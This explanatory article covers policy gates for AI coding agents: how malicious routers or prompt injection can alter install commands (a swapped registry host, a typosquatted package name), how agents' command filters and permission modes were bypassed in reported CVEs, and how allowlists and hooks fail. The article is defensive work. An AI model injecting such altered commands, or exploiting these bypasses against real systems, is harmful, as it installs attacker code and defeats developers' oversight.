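# Policy gates on shell and package-install commands run by AI agents

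## How an agent's command can be changed before it runs

In an AI coding agent, a language model chooses actions, such as shell commands, and software carries them out on a developer's computer. Agents use shell commands to search files, run tests and install packages, the ready-made code that most software depends on. Commands that download or install something carry a particular risk because they bring code from elsewhere onto the machine and may run it immediately. A policy gate on the developer's machine compares each risky command with written rules and refuses what the rules do not permit. Developers need one because the command arrives as text from a distant server, and anyone who can change that text on the way can change what the machine installs.

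### From the model to the shell

A coding agent works in a loop, sending the model the conversation so far and a list of tools it may use. The model replies, and the agent's software runs whatever tool call the reply contains, then sends the result back to the model for the next round. Xie, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *The Proxy Knows Too Much*, call the coding agent the most acute case of the danger because its tools run on the developer's machine with the developer's permissions. A command can read any file the developer can read, including stored passwords and keys.

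Suppose a developer asks an agent to repair a failing build, and the model works out that a Python library named `requests` is missing. The model's response has two parts. One is a sentence or two of prose for the developer. The other is a tool call, a structured message, usually in JSON, that tells the agent's software which action to run and with what arguments. In simplified form:

```
{"tool": "shell",
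 "command": "pip install --index-url https://packages.example.com/simple requests"}
```

`pip` is Python's package installer. The address after `--index-url` points to a package registry, a server that stores packages and supplies them by name. The registry in this example is an invented company server that mirrors PyPI, the main public registry for Python, where anyone can publish a package under an unclaimed name. The address and the package name, which is the last word of the command, are its operands, the parts that identify what it acts on.

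*Rewriting the Response Path* (Luo, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) represents a response as a pair, r = (x, c), where x is the text the developer reads and c is the tool call the software executes. Only c determines the next action, so the software will execute a harmful tool call even if the text beside it is reassuring.

Agents can ask the developer to confirm a command before running it. With automatic approval, commands run as soon as they arrive, so nobody reads an install command before the shell runs it. Confirming every step is slow, and Fu, Li and colleagues (2026) say in *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* that most users of coding agents choose automatic approval.

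### The router and its two encrypted connections

Many agents reach the model's provider through a router, a service that forwards requests and responses and can read and change both. The router checks the caller's key, picks an account with a provider, attaches that account's key, forwards the request, passes back the reply and records the usage for billing. People use routers to reach many models with one key, switch models when one fails, pay less, or get access from a region that a provider does not serve.

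The arrangement is common. LiteLLM, an open-source router, has over 240 million downloads of its ready-to-run image on Docker Hub, according to Fu and colleagues. Among the 60 most-used applications on OpenRouter, a large commercial router, Luo and colleagues found 25 interactive agents or front ends where a custom address made sense, and 23 of them accepted the user's own key or address. Setting up a router takes a line or two. In Anthropic's agent Claude Code, for example, the user puts the router's web address in one variable and the router's key in another, according to Anthropic's documentation.

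That setting is also why encryption does not help. Web traffic is encrypted with TLS (transport layer security), which protects a connection between two endpoints from outsiders, but the developer has named the router as the endpoint. The router decrypts the agent's request and sends it to the provider over a second encrypted connection. It then decrypts the provider's response and re-encrypts it for the agent, so it holds the install command as plain text in between. *HTTP Message Signatures* (Backman, Richer and Sporny, 2024), an internet standard, states that where a gateway ends one TLS connection and starts another, TLS cannot guarantee that a message crosses the whole path unaltered.

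The user has given the router access, so it does not need to break the cipher, forge a certificate or hijack the network route, as an ordinary eavesdropper would. Stricter certificate checks would not help, because they can prove only that the agent has reached the router the developer chose, not what the router did with the response.

A request may pass through more than one router. Crosley (2026), in *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet*, relays the example of a developer who buys access from a reseller on Taobao, the Chinese marketplace. The reseller pools keys from a second supplier, the supplier goes through OpenRouter, and OpenRouter passes the request to the company that hosts the model. Each of the four can read and rewrite everything, but the developer's settings show only the reseller.

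An agent could detect a changed command if the provider attached a signature, a cryptographic mark covering the tool call, for the agent to check before acting. Liu, Shou and colleagues reported in *Your Agent Is Mine* (April 2026) that no provider enforced any such link between the model and the client. In the notation of Luo and colleagues, the agent runs c without checking whether the model produced c. This does little harm on a direct connection, where there is no third party to interfere and TLS covers the whole route, but agents also skip the check when a router is present.

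Liu and colleagues confirmed this by building a malicious router and connecting four agent frameworks to it, including Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. None of the four checked whether the response had been altered. Commands with an altered package name reached the agents in valid form 99.6% of the time, and other altered commands always did. Crosley points out that these figures count only commands that reached the agents. A permission prompt or a restriction on the machine might still have stopped them from running.

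### What a dishonest router can change

In this attack, the provider is honest, the model wrote a harmless command, and the developer's machine and agent software are uncompromised. The attacker controls a router on the path and can replace any field with another that the agent's software will accept as well formed. The table shows two ways to alter the example.

| Version | Registry address | Package name |
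|---|---|---|
| As the model wrote it | packages.example.com | `requests` |
| With the address altered | packages.example.net | `requests` |
| With the name altered | packages.example.com | `reqeusts` |

Payload injection means changing or adding a tool call so that the client runs the attacker's command. For example, the router can change the download address in an install command. The developer still sees `pip` installing `requests`, but the code comes from a server the attacker chose. The router can also leave the model's command unchanged and append a second one. Fu and colleagues describe a subtler version in which the router has the model's explanation rewritten to fit the new command, so a developer who compares the two finds no mismatch.

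Dependency substitution is payload injection that changes only the package name in an install command. The attacker must already have published a lookalike package, with a name close to that of a well-known package. The misspelling in the table is Liu and colleagues' own example. The program, option and registry address are all what the developer would expect, so a check that looks only at web addresses passes the command. The damage can outlast the session, because the package stays on the machine and later work may use it.

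Liu and colleagues treat conditional delivery separately because it concerns when the router makes a change and can accompany either kind of change. The router forwards everything unchanged until a condition is met, such as the use of a certain tool, a keyword, a time of day, a number of past requests or signs that the session runs on automatic approval. Testing a router before use is therefore less reliable. If a router waits for 50 requests, a test of ten will not reveal the problem, and no test of fixed length can rule out a longer wait or a condition the tester did not think of.

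A router can also copy secrets from the traffic without changing anything. A check on commands can't prevent this, because the secrets have left the machine before any command comes back.

An attacker can compromise a router without owning it. In March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of LiteLLM on PyPI, and Help Net Security's *Command integrity breaks in the LLM routing layer* notes that the inserted code had access to every request and response on the affected systems. Even a team that ran its own copy of LiteLLM could have been exposed.

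Prompt injection produces the same bad command, and the two cases look alike at the shell. The attacker plants instructions in something the model reads, such as a web page or a file in a code repository, and the model itself writes the harmful tool call. A provider's signature would not help, because the command really did come from the model. eWeek's *Clean GitHub Repo Attack Exposes AI Coding Agent Risk* (2026) covers a demonstration by Mozilla's 0DIN in which a clean-looking repository exposed Claude Code to this kind of attack.

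### How often routers have been caught

Liu and colleagues made the first systematic measurement of malicious routers. They bought 28 paid routers from sellers on Taobao, Xianyu and Shopify and collected 400 free ones from public communities. For each router, they opened an account, ran a coding agent through it in an isolated environment, executed every tool call that came back, and watched for unexpected network connections, file changes and processes. A separate analysis agent reviewed anything suspicious. They counted a router as injecting only if it rewrote a tool call into an attacker-controlled command or package. They also sent Amazon Web Services (AWS) keys through the routers as bait to see whether anyone would use them.

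| Behaviour | Paid routers (of 28) | Free routers (of 400) |
|---|---|---|
| Injected malicious code into tool calls | 1 | 8 |
| Injected only under chosen conditions | 0 | 2 |
| Used a planted AWS key | 0 | 17 |
| Emptied a planted Ethereum wallet | 0 | 1 |

In total, nine routers injected code. Two did so only under certain conditions, evidently to avoid detection. One of these began only after 50 requests. The other acted only in sessions that appeared to be on automatic approval, and only on projects written in Rust or Go.

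Nine in 428 is about 2%, but that figure shouldn't be generalized to all routers. The sample came from grey markets, mostly Chinese-language ones, and two open-source templates account for most of the free routers. The study did not cover company gateways, invitation-only services, OpenRouter or LiteLLM. Within the sample, the count is more likely too low than too high, because a router that alters commands only under certain conditions would have gone undetected if the tests never met those conditions.

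In a newer study, *What the Middleman Delivers*, Wu, Zhao and colleagues (2026) tested 20 routers that sell access to GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5. They confirmed no injected content in 3,332 responses to harmless requests about code and setup. This sample was not random either. It favoured services with English websites that take cards or PayPal, so it probably overlaps little with the market that Liu and colleagues searched. Wu and colleagues also executed nothing, planted no secrets and sent each request on its own, so many conditional attacks would not have been triggered. They warn against pooling the two sets of results. The two studies show that malicious routers exist and that many routers injected nothing detectable in simple tests, but neither supports an estimate of how likely a randomly chosen router is to be malicious.

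Wu and colleagues found that four routers returned a total of 30 tool calls, although the request had told the model to make none. The calls named a harmless placeholder tool, and 24 of them came from a single router. None appeared when they repeated the test 11 to 18 days later. The cause could have been the router, the model or a fault in translating between formats. Whatever the cause, the restriction in the request did not hold, and the researchers conclude that the client has to enforce such restrictions itself.

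In a second investigation, Liu and colleagues studied what happens behind routers that nobody designed to be malicious. They set up badly secured routers as decoys on 20 web domains and 20 internet addresses. Strangers found the decoys, and other people's routing services began sending real traffic through them. The decoys handled about 2 billion tokens (the fragments of text that models process) and exposed 99 credentials across 440 sessions of Codex. The developers behind those sessions had presumably configured some other router and could not know where it sent their traffic.

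Whoever held the decoy could have injected a command into any of the 440 sessions. In 401 of them (91%), commands were already approved automatically, so even a crudely altered install command would have run without a human check. The percentage describes people whose traffic ended up in resold and reused routers. They may be less cautious than most, so it is weak evidence about developers at large. But it does show that agents run commands without human checks in the part of the market where Liu and colleagues found dishonest routers.

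### What a policy gate promises

A policy gate uses written rules to decide whether a tool call may run. It acts after the model's response has reached the machine and before the shell runs the command, which is the last point where the developer still has control. Many of the rules are allowlists, which list the domains, packages or commands that the gate permits. A fail-closed gate blocks any command it cannot parse or does not recognise, while a fail-open gate lets such commands through.

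In the example command, the gate identifies a `pip` install, the registry packages.example.com and the package `requests`. It allows the command if both the registry and the package are on the allowlist. If the address has been altered, the gate blocks the command because the new registry is not on the list. If the package name has been altered, the registry is still allowed, so the gate blocks the command only if it has a list of packages as well as a list of domains.

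The gate has no copy of the command the model wrote, so it cannot compare that command with the one it receives. Fu and colleagues argue that allowlists, like other client-side safeguards, depend on the response arriving unaltered from the provider. That seems too strong for this gate, which would refuse packages.example.net no matter who put it in the command. But the argument does hold for permitted commands. If a router replaces `requests` with another package on the list, or repeats an approved install when nobody asked for it, the gate will allow the command.

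The gate guarantees only that the commands it checks and allows satisfy its rules. How much protection this gives depends on the rules and the attacker. In Liu and colleagues' own trials, a gate stopped every straightforward injection but failed every time against an attacker who chose commands to satisfy its rules. The gate also does not establish who wrote a command, so it will block the misspelt package name `reqeusts` even when the model made the typing error itself, and it will allow a correctly spelt install that the model never requested.

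## Writing rules that allow, ask or deny

A policy gate returns one of three verdicts on a command: allow, ask or deny. An ask verdict holds the command until the developer approves or rejects it. The gate has to determine what the command would do before it can apply any rule, and many of the flaws that researchers reported in 2026 are in that step.

### The gate as an algorithm

A small gate for shell and install commands takes seven steps:

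1. Pick out the high-risk tools. The rules list the few tools that can do no harm, such as one that lists the project's files, and the gate treats every other tool as high-risk. A list of dangerous tools would let a newly added one through unchecked.
2. Split the command. One line can hold several commands joined by operators such as `&&`, and the gate judges each part.
3. Identify the program that each part would start.
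4. Extract the operands: domains, packages and paths.
5. Compare each operand with its allowlist.
6. Combine the results, so that a single denial decides.
7. Refuse the whole command if any earlier step failed.

The developer keeps the rules in a file. This one continues the example of a company registry at packages.example.com:

```
low_risk_tools: [list_files]
domains:        [packages.example.com]
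packages:       [requests, pytest]
workspace:      /home/dev/project
programs:
  cd:   {operand: path}
  pip:  {subcommand: install, operand: package,
         options: {--index-url: domain}}
```

In the pseudocode below, `strictest` returns the most severe verdict in a list, with deny above ask and ask above allow. It raises an error if the list is empty.

```
check(call, developer_present):
    if call.tool in low_risk_tools: return ALLOW
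    try:
        parts = split(call.command)        # unclear syntax: error
        verdict = strictest(judge(p) for p in parts)
    on any error:
        return DENY
    if verdict == ASK and not developer_present: return DENY
    return verdict

judge(part):
    rule = programs[part.program]          # no rule: error
    targets = extract(part, rule)          # unknown option: error
    if targets is empty: return ASK
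    return strictest(compare(t) for t in targets)

compare(target):
    domain:   ALLOW if in domains,       else DENY
    package:  ALLOW if in packages,      else ASK
    path:     ALLOW if inside workspace, else DENY
```

A working rules file needs many more entries, including programs such as `ls` that may run without any operand.

The gate has to compare values exactly. For a web address, it should extract the host name and check whether it equals an entry in the list, because searching the whole address for a permitted name would also accept a longer host name that contains it. pip ignores case in package names and treats hyphens and underscores alike, so the gate should convert names to one standard form before comparing them. For paths, it should follow symbolic links (files that point to other files) before deciding whether a path is inside the workspace.

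Some commands omit an operand. If an install command names no registry, pip takes the address from a configuration file or an environment variable, so the gate must look it up there or require the command to name it. `npm install`, the JavaScript equivalent, installs whatever the project's own files list when no package name follows it. Until version 3.25.23, the coding agent Roo Code had `npm install` on its default list of commands that could run without approval. OSV's *CVE-2025-58374* (2025), an entry in a public database of software flaws, records that a malicious project could use this to run its own install scripts. No rule covered what `npm install` would install, so the pseudocode returns ask when it finds no operand.

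Rules that match a program's name need the same care. OSV's *CVE-2026-55581* (2026) reports that mcp-shell, a server that runs shell commands for agents, checked only the first word of each command and included a shell in its default allowlist. Because a shell runs any text passed to it, agents could use that entry to run commands that weren't on the list. Policy writers can prevent this by leaving shells off the list or by checking the text passed to them as a separate command.

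Settings written in front of a command can also disguise it. Warp, a development environment with built-in agents, used to check commands against a denylist (commands that need confirmation) before handling such settings. Rapid7's *CVE-2026-48721* explains how this let a listed command pass as an unlisted one. Warp has fixed the flaw. A gate should remove the settings before it identifies the program, and refuse any setting the rules do not name.

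A gate can stop checking a command as soon as it finds a reason to deny it, but it must finish every check before returning allow or ask. Enginsight's *CVE-2026-35570* reports that one configuration of OpenClaude, an open-source coding agent, returned allow before the path check had run. Returning ask early could hide a denial later in the command.

### Four commands through the gate

The table shows how the gate treats four commands that arrive while the developer is present.

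| Command | What the gate extracts | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| `pip install --index-url https://packages.example.com/simple requests` | Listed domain, listed package | Allow |
| `pip install --index-url https://packages.example.net/simple requests` | Unlisted domain, listed package | Deny |
| `pip install --index-url https://packages.example.com/simple tabulate` | Listed domain, unlisted package | Ask |
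| `cd app && pip install --index-url https://packages.example.com/simple $(cat wanted.txt)` | Path inside the workspace, then an install with no readable package name | Deny |

The install from packages.example.net fails although `requests` is on the list, because the denial for the domain outweighs the approval for the package.

`tabulate` is a real library for printing tables that this team has not listed yet. The gate would treat it the same way as the misspelt `reqeusts`, because it checks only whether a name is on the list. If the gate asks, the developer has to tell the two apart, which takes time for every new dependency. If commands run on automatic approval, nobody can answer, so the gate denies both.

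The last command contains a command substitution, so the shell runs `cat wanted.txt` first and puts the file's contents in its place. The text that the gate receives doesn't include the package names. The gate could open the file itself, but then it would be imitating the shell, and the file could change before the install ran. The gate therefore refuses the whole line, including the harmless `cd`.

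A refusal should include a reason that the agent can act on. If the message says that the gate cannot read command substitutions, the agent can read the package names from the file and resend the install command with the names written out, so that the gate can check them. However, a dishonest router can also learn the rules from these messages and act as an adaptive attacker, choosing commands that satisfy the rules.

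### Matching text and parsing syntax

The hardest parts of the pseudocode are `split` and `extract`, which turn a line of text into programs and operands. The simplest method is to search the text for patterns. *AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) describes a gate that does this, with 170 rules for dangerous commands such as deleting the whole disk or piping a download straight into a shell.

Bash, a widely used shell, fills in variables, removes quotation marks and decodes escaped characters before running a command. The same command can therefore be written in many ways, and a pattern that matches one of them misses the rest. AgentTrust applies nine kinds of rewriting to the command text, checks the original and every rewritten version, and keeps the most severe verdict, so no rewrite can hide a danger found in another version.

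Yang preferred this to a full shell parser because Bash has so much unusual syntax, and because developers of a parser would be tempted to run parts of a command to see what they produce. AgentTrust gave the right verdict on 96.7% of 630 test commands, and on about 93% of disguised commands. Yang had already added rules for gaps that the same tests revealed, so it would probably do worse on new disguises. By default, AgentTrust also allows any command that matches no pattern, so a command written in a way nobody foresaw goes through.

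Patterns work better when they describe the permitted commands, because a command with an unforeseen spelling is then refused. Such a pattern has to match the whole command, and the part for the package name should allow only letters, digits and the few punctuation marks that real names contain. These patterns are easy to check but rigid, and a harmless install can fail just because two options are in an unexpected order.

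SC Media's *Shell injection flaw found in 10 of 11 open-source AI agents* (2026) reports on a survey in which the security firm Adversa AI got around the command filters of ten agents. Some bypasses nested one command inside another. Others used the destructive options of ordinary utilities such as `find`, which searches for files but can also delete them. To stop these, a rule has to cover a program's options as well as its name. Filters that split the command into words did better than plain string matching but still missed some bypasses. Only one agent, Continue, blocked every bypass Adversa tried, by combining several kinds of evaluation.

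A parser applies the shell's grammar. It can tell a semicolon inside quotation marks, which is only text, from one that separates two commands. The parser protects the machine only if it agrees with the shell, and Roo Code's parser disagreed with bash in several places:

- It did not know one of bash's pipe operators, which connect two commands, so it approved a whole line on the strength of the permitted command at the start. VulnCheck's *Roo-Code 3.54.0 Auto-Approve Bypass via Shell Command Pipe Operator* describes this flaw.
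- It placed the start of a comment differently from bash, and so ignored text that bash went on to execute, according to VulnCheck's *Roo-Code 3.54.0 Auto-Approve Bypass via Shell Parser Word-Boundary Mismatch*.
- It replaced certain variable expressions with placeholders before it looked for nested commands, so a command inside such an expression escaped the check. The record is NVD's *CVE-2026-63108 Detail*, from the US government's vulnerability database.

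It is safer to put the grammar itself on an allowlist than to repair these one at a time, because a developer who repairs them individually still doesn't know how many remain. The gate accepts plain words, simple quotation marks and one or two operators, and treats every other construct as unreadable. It then only has to parse that small part of the language the same way bash does.

### When the approved text is not what runs

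Five security advisories on coding agents and a toolkit for building them appeared between 13 and 16 October 2026. Cornelißen (2026), in *Coding-Agenten*, found the same fault behind all five: what ran was different from what the software had checked.

| Product | What the software checked | What could run | Remedy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mistral Vibe | The permitted command that its parser found | That command and another hidden in a variable | Version 2.25.4 |
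| Roo Code | The command with its output redirections removed | A command that the user had forbidden | None; replace it |
| JetBrains Junie CLI | No effective check | Code from an untrusted project's settings | Version 26.8.3 |
| Z.ai ZCode | Nothing | Commands from the project's settings | Unclear; avoid unknown projects |
| Claude Agent SDK for Python | Tool permissions, but not the session ID | Commands brought in through the session ID | Version 0.2.121 |

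Mistral Vibe's parser checked the command as fixed text. Bash can execute text stored in a variable while the command is running, so text hidden there became a command only after the check. A gate can't predict everything a variable will contain, but it can refuse the constructs that turn stored text into commands. Mistral released its fix on 12 September, a month before the advisory came out.

Roo Code removed redirections, which send a command's output to a file, before checking the command against its allowlist. It also removed text that was not a complete redirection. The remaining text looked like a permitted command, but bash parsed the original text differently and ran something else. The attack works only if automatic approval is on, and the command could come from prompt injection or a router.

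Roo Code will not get a fix, because its maintainers archived the project in May 2026. The last release, version 3.54.0, is affected. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-81835* (2026), a notice from Spain's cybersecurity institute about an earlier flaw, quotes the maintainers calling Roo Code "a project we no longer support". Its approval list will therefore get weaker each time someone publishes another command that Roo Code and the shell parse differently.

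In Junie and ZCode, the command came from the project's settings, so a gate that reads only the model's tool calls would miss it. Both agents support MCP (the Model Context Protocol), a standard for connecting agents to outside tools. When an MCP server runs on the developer's own machine, the project's settings include the command that starts it. ZCode ran that command as soon as the developer opened the project. The fix is to treat these start commands like any other command and ask before running them. Claude Code asks in interactive sessions, Cornelißen notes, but loads the servers without asking when it runs unattended.

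The flaw in the Claude Agent SDK mattered only to applications that accepted a session ID from outsiders. The SDK passed the ID to a command-line program, which read some values as options, and one of those options could run a command the attacker chose. An install gate faces the same problem with package names, so it should refuse any name that does not start with a letter or digit, because pip might read that name as an option.

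Pasting a checked operand back into shell text can undo the check. In OpenCode, another coding agent, a web address could pass every format check and still contain text that PowerShell, the Windows shell, would execute. Pillar Security, the firm that found the flaw, recommends starting the program directly and passing the address as a separate argument, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Warn OpenCode Quietly Patched Critical RCE Flaw* (2026). A gate that follows this advice runs the same list of arguments it checked, so no shell can reinterpret them. The agent loses pipes and other shell features unless its software supplies them.

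### Judging a structured action

In October 2026, Jing (2026), in *What a Policy Gate Can and Cannot Know*, took the separation further with a gate that never receives shell text. A component called the realiser first turns the command into a structured record, and the gate judges the record. For the command `cp report.txt backup`, which copies a file into a folder, a simplified record would be:

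```
status:    resolved
verb:      cp
operands:  report.txt, backup
targets:   /home/dev/project/report.txt   working area
           /home/dev/project/backup       working area
```

The realiser follows any symbolic links and records the real locations as the targets. If `backup` were a link to a system folder, the record would list the system folder as the target, and the gate would apply its rules to that folder. The full record also includes any variables set at the start of the command line and how many targets a pattern such as `*` added. If the command gives the program by its path, the record includes a hash calculated from the program file's contents.

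The gate applies seven rules to each record:

1. Fail closed on anything the realiser could not resolve, and on errors inside the gate itself.
2. Restrict sensitive verbs according to their effect, whatever their names.
3. Identify the program by its name, its position in the command, and the contents and attributes of its file.
4. Judge each target by its zone. Jing's test machine has five zones: a working area, a protected area, an area that only the administrator can change, a writable area outside the workspace, and everything else.
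5. Protect the top folder of the workspace itself.
6. Take account of how many objects the command affects, including those that a pattern added.
7. Compare the objects affected with the objects that the request declared, and require the declaration to cover all of them.

The contents of a program file expose a renamed copy, but only if someone maintains a list of known programs for comparison.

The realiser gives pipelines, command substitutions and commands grouped in brackets or braces a separate status, undecidable, and the rule on unresolved input then applies. It splits up commands separated by semicolons or line breaks and evaluates each one. If any command is denied, the whole sequence is denied. Otherwise, a sequence that affects more than one object goes to a person for review. Of 216 commands that Jing carried over from an earlier Windows benchmark, 15 were undecidable and 10 were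 sequences. The benchmark contains many attacks, so these numbers can't be used to estimate how often an ordinary developer would have a command refused.

The realiser still has to read shell text, and Jing found faults there. When a command had broken syntax, the realiser lost the error message and passed on an empty list of arguments. The gate then had no target to check, so it let the command through. Jing changed the realiser to report the failure, which the gate treats as a refusal. In another trial, Jing relaxed the rule that sends every action without a target to review. A command to delete a folder and its contents then went through because the realiser had failed to recognise the target. The rule had also been catching extraction errors, so Jing restored it only for commands with an operand that looks like a path.

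Instead of shell text, software can send the gate a structured request with a named operation, full paths and typed arguments. Shell text and structured requests for the same operation must then produce identical records. In an early version of Jing's system, the two routes assigned different roles to one field, and the gate gave the same request opposite verdicts depending on which route it took.

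In this design, approving a command produces a credential tied to the verb, the full list of arguments, and the identity and contents of the files. If any of these change before execution, the credential is no longer valid. Because the credential works only once, a router also can't repeat an approved command.

Jing's gate is not ready to check installs. It models files and programs but not network requests, so it can't distinguish packages.example.com from packages.example.net. A developer would have to add domains and packages as target types, as the pseudocode above does. The gate also doesn't carry information from one command to the next. If one command sets a variable and the next uses it, the gate evaluates the second without that value, so an install gate should deny both. Jing tested the rules by deliberately introducing faults into them and by running scripts with and without the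 gate.

### Fail-closed and fail-open

Jing's gate refuses when its own code fails. Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026), in *Reason Less, Verify More*, made the opposite choice for a simulated airline's customer-service agent. They wrote four gates, each a short program that takes the tool's name, its arguments and the state of the booking database and returns allow or reject. One rejects cancellations that the fare rules do not allow. If a gate crashes, the software records the error and lets the call proceed, because the researchers did not want bugs in the gates to block legitimate work.

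The worry about wrong refusals was justified. The cancellation gate was right in all 161 of its rejections, but another of the four gates was right in only 5% of its rejections. Even so, the four gates together raised the share of tasks that GPT-4o mini completed from 29.6% to 42.0%.

A rough calculation shows what the choice depends on. Let q be the share of unreadable commands that are malicious, L the loss from running a malicious command, and B the cost of blocking a harmless one. Refusing an unreadable command costs (1 − q)B on average, and allowing it costs qL. Refusing is cheaper when

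q > B / (B + L).

Suppose a developer loses five minutes to a wrong refusal and 40 hours of work to a compromised machine. Refusing unreadable commands then saves time on average if more than one in 481 of them (5/2,405, or about 0.2%) is malicious.

The calculation treats q as fixed, which is reasonable for the airline because its customers are not trying to crash the gates and the tool calls arrive with their arguments already separated. But a router that writes shell commands can choose q. If the gate fails open, an attacker who knows this will write every malicious command in a form the gate cannot read, bypassing the other rules. Shell and install commands from a router therefore need a fail-closed gate.

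Failing open is reasonable when errors come from bugs that no attacker can trigger, and when someone can reverse a wrong action or another control backs up the gate. It also suits a trial period, in which the gate only records what it would have refused. It does not suit commands that look harmless, because a gate that can't read a command can't check whether it is harmless.

AgentTrust sends a command to review if the gate hits an error, but it lets a command that matches no rule run by default. The user can change that default. AgentTrust also has a fourth verdict, warn, which lets the command run with a note attached and so gives no more protection than allow.

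A gate can also fail open by accident. In the agent OpenClaw, one branch of the code that read shell commands lacked the expected allowlist decision, so commands that took that branch could run without approval (CIRCL, *GHSA-v383-2wgg-v483*, 2026). A developer can guard against this by setting the verdict to deny by default and changing it only after a check succeeds. A forgotten branch then blocks harmless commands, which users will notice and report.

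### Faults in the rules themselves

A gate that parses every command correctly can still apply a bad rule. In *NOMOS*, Yu, Kim and Choi (2026) used a language model to turn written company policies into rules for tool calls. One policy required the agent to authenticate the customer before doing anything else. The resulting rule blocked every tool, including the two lookup tools that perform authentication, until the customer was authenticated, so no conversation could get past that point. Other rules referred to arguments that their tools did not have.

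Structural faults like these affected 37% of the candidate rules for an airline and 13% of those for a shop. Handwritten rules may go wrong less often, but the same mistakes are easy to make in an install gate. The option that names a registry is `--index-url` in pip and `--registry` in npm. A rule that looks for `--registry` in pip commands will never match, but the developer may believe it is checking every address.

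Yu and colleagues found the structural faults by comparing each rule with the descriptions of the tools it governed, without using a language model. Some rules had the right structure but still refused legitimate work. To find those, the researchers replayed recorded sessions through the gate. One rule refused 95.9% of the calls to a tool in sessions where the agent had completed its task. The developer of an install gate can do the same on a small scale by storing with each rule one command it must allow and one it must refuse, then running all of these commands after each change to the rules file.

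## Placing the gate between the response and the shell

A well-tested rules file gives no protection if commands can reach the shell without passing through the gate. A developer can put the gate in any of five places:

| Place | Commands that reach the gate | Who could switch it off |
|---|---|---|
| Instructions in the prompt | None | The router, or any text that persuades the model |
| Inside the agent program | Tool calls that the program submits to the check | The user, or anyone who can change the program or its settings |
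| A hook before execution | Tool calls that match the hook's filter | Anyone who can edit the hook's script or settings |
| A wrapper round the shell or package manager | Commands that find the wrapper by name, including those inside scripts | Any process that can change the search path or start the real program directly |
| A separate process that alone can execute | Every command the agent starts | Whoever controls that process and its policy |

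### Instructions in the prompt

The weakest gate is a prompt instruction to install packages only from packages.example.com. The model may obey it, but the router changes the command afterward, and no program checks the new command against the instruction. The router can also delete the instruction from the request. Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code warns that instructions in a prompt or a project's CLAUDE.md file affect what the model tries to do, but not what the program allows.

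### What the built-in permission modes stopped

Coding agents have permission modes that set which actions an agent may take without asking. In July 2026, Fu and colleagues injected malicious tool calls through a router into ten configurations of four agents. No configuration stopped any of the calls.

| Agent | Restricted or reviewed | Everything approved |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | plan, acceptEdits, auto | bypassPermissions |
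| Codex | Auto | Full Access |
| Cursor | Auto-review | Run Everything |
| OpenCode | Plan | Build, with all permissions allowed |

The result is unsurprising for the four configurations that approve everything. For the others, Fu and colleagues give two reasons. In Claude Code's plan mode, the agent is supposed to read files and propose changes without making any, but only the prompt imposed this limit, so the program executed the injected calls. In the modes with automatic review, the agent sent its review requests through the same router that had injected the command, so the router could tamper with the review too.

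Neither reason explains the result for acceptEdits. According to Anthropic's current documentation, that mode approves file edits and a few file commands such as `mkdir`, so it would not approve an install. Fu and colleagues do not discuss the discrepancy, and they caution that their figures depend on the configuration.

The experiment also left out two Claude Code modes. In the default mode, a person answers repeated prompts, and in dontAsk, the outcome depends on which actions the user has approved in advance. The experiment therefore doesn't measure how well a developer who reads every command would do. Few developers seem to work that way. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users reject 3% of individual permission requests, compared with 39% of the plans the agent presents for approval. The 3% suggests that many users approve out of habit, though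 it doesn't prove that they miss attacks, since most requests are presumably harmless.

Claude Code has changed since July. Its plan mode now blocks file edits until the user approves the plan, and sends shell commands to an automatic reviewer or the user. Neither protection applies in an interactive terminal session where the user has made bypassPermissions available. In auto mode, the agent can have the provider's server review actions as part of its ordinary model requests, even when those requests go through a router. Claude Code blocks the action if the response breaks off before the verdict arrives or the verdict is unreadable. Blocking in those cases does not protect against a forged verdict, and the router still carries both the command and the verdict.

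### Checks inside the agent program

A rule that the agent program applies on the developer's machine does not depend on the router. Claude Code's deny rules hold in every mode, including bypassPermissions. Its allow rules have no effect in that mode because nothing needs their approval, so an allowlist no longer restricts the agent. Denying everything and then allowing exceptions doesn't work either, because a deny rule always overrides an allow rule.

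According to Anthropic, 25% of interactive sessions started in this mode. An administrator can disable it through managed settings, which users cannot override.

AgentTrust also runs inside the agent's process. Yang acknowledges that a malicious agent program can avoid the check by not calling the checker. A router changes only text, so at first it can't stop the agent from calling the checker, and the check still runs on the first injected command. But if one harmful command gets through, it may alter the agent's program or settings so that later commands can skip the check. Yang notes that enforcement from outside the process requires a different design, such as restricted execution or a check in the operating system's kernel.

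### A hook before execution

A hook is a program that the agent starts at a set point in its work. Claude Code's PreToolUse hook and Cursor's beforeShellExecution hook run before a command does. The agent sends the hook the proposed call as JSON, and the hook replies with a verdict. This is the easiest place to install the gate from the previous section, because the developer can write it in any language and leave the agent unmodified. In Claude Code, the settings could look like this:

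```
{"hooks": {"PreToolUse": [{
  "matcher": "*",
  "hooks": [{
    "type": "command",
    "command": "/opt/gate/check",
    "args": [],
    "onFailure": "block"
  }]
}]}}
```

The asterisk sends every kind of tool call to the gate, including calls from subagents, the helper agents that the main agent starts. A narrower filter can miss commands. According to Anthropic's hooks reference, before version 2.1.314 a hook that named only the Bash tool did not run on shell commands started by Claude Code's Monitor tool. Cursor's *Hooks* gives an example filter that starts the hook only when the command contains `curl`, `wget` or `nc`. With that filter, the gate would never receive an ordinary `pip install`. Developers should put rules about specific commands in the gate instead.

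The `onFailure` line makes the hook fail closed. Without it, Claude Code normally runs the command if the hook crashes, exceeds its time limit or has a mistyped path. Exit code 1, which conventionally signals failure, doesn't block the command either, but exit code 2 does. `onFailure` requires Claude Code 2.1.295 or later. Cursor also fails open by default, and its equivalent setting is `failClosed: true`.

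These defaults have caused failures. In *beforeShellExecution hook*, a 2026 thread on Cursor's support forum, a user reported that Cursor ran a command because the hook's reply was malformed JSON. The workaround was to build the reply with a JSON tool instead of pasting the command into a text template. With a template, an attacker who can choose the command's text might break the reply on purpose.

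Another thread, *Hooks not firing. Cannot have guardrails*, describes a failure inside the script. On Windows, Cursor put an invisible character at the start of the JSON it sent to the hook. The script couldn't parse the input, and its error handler returned allow. When the user tested the script by hand, the character was missing and the script correctly denied the command. A setting such as `failClosed` can't reliably catch this kind of error, because the agent receives a valid approval. The script's error handler has to return deny, and the developer has to test the hook through the agent as well as by hand.

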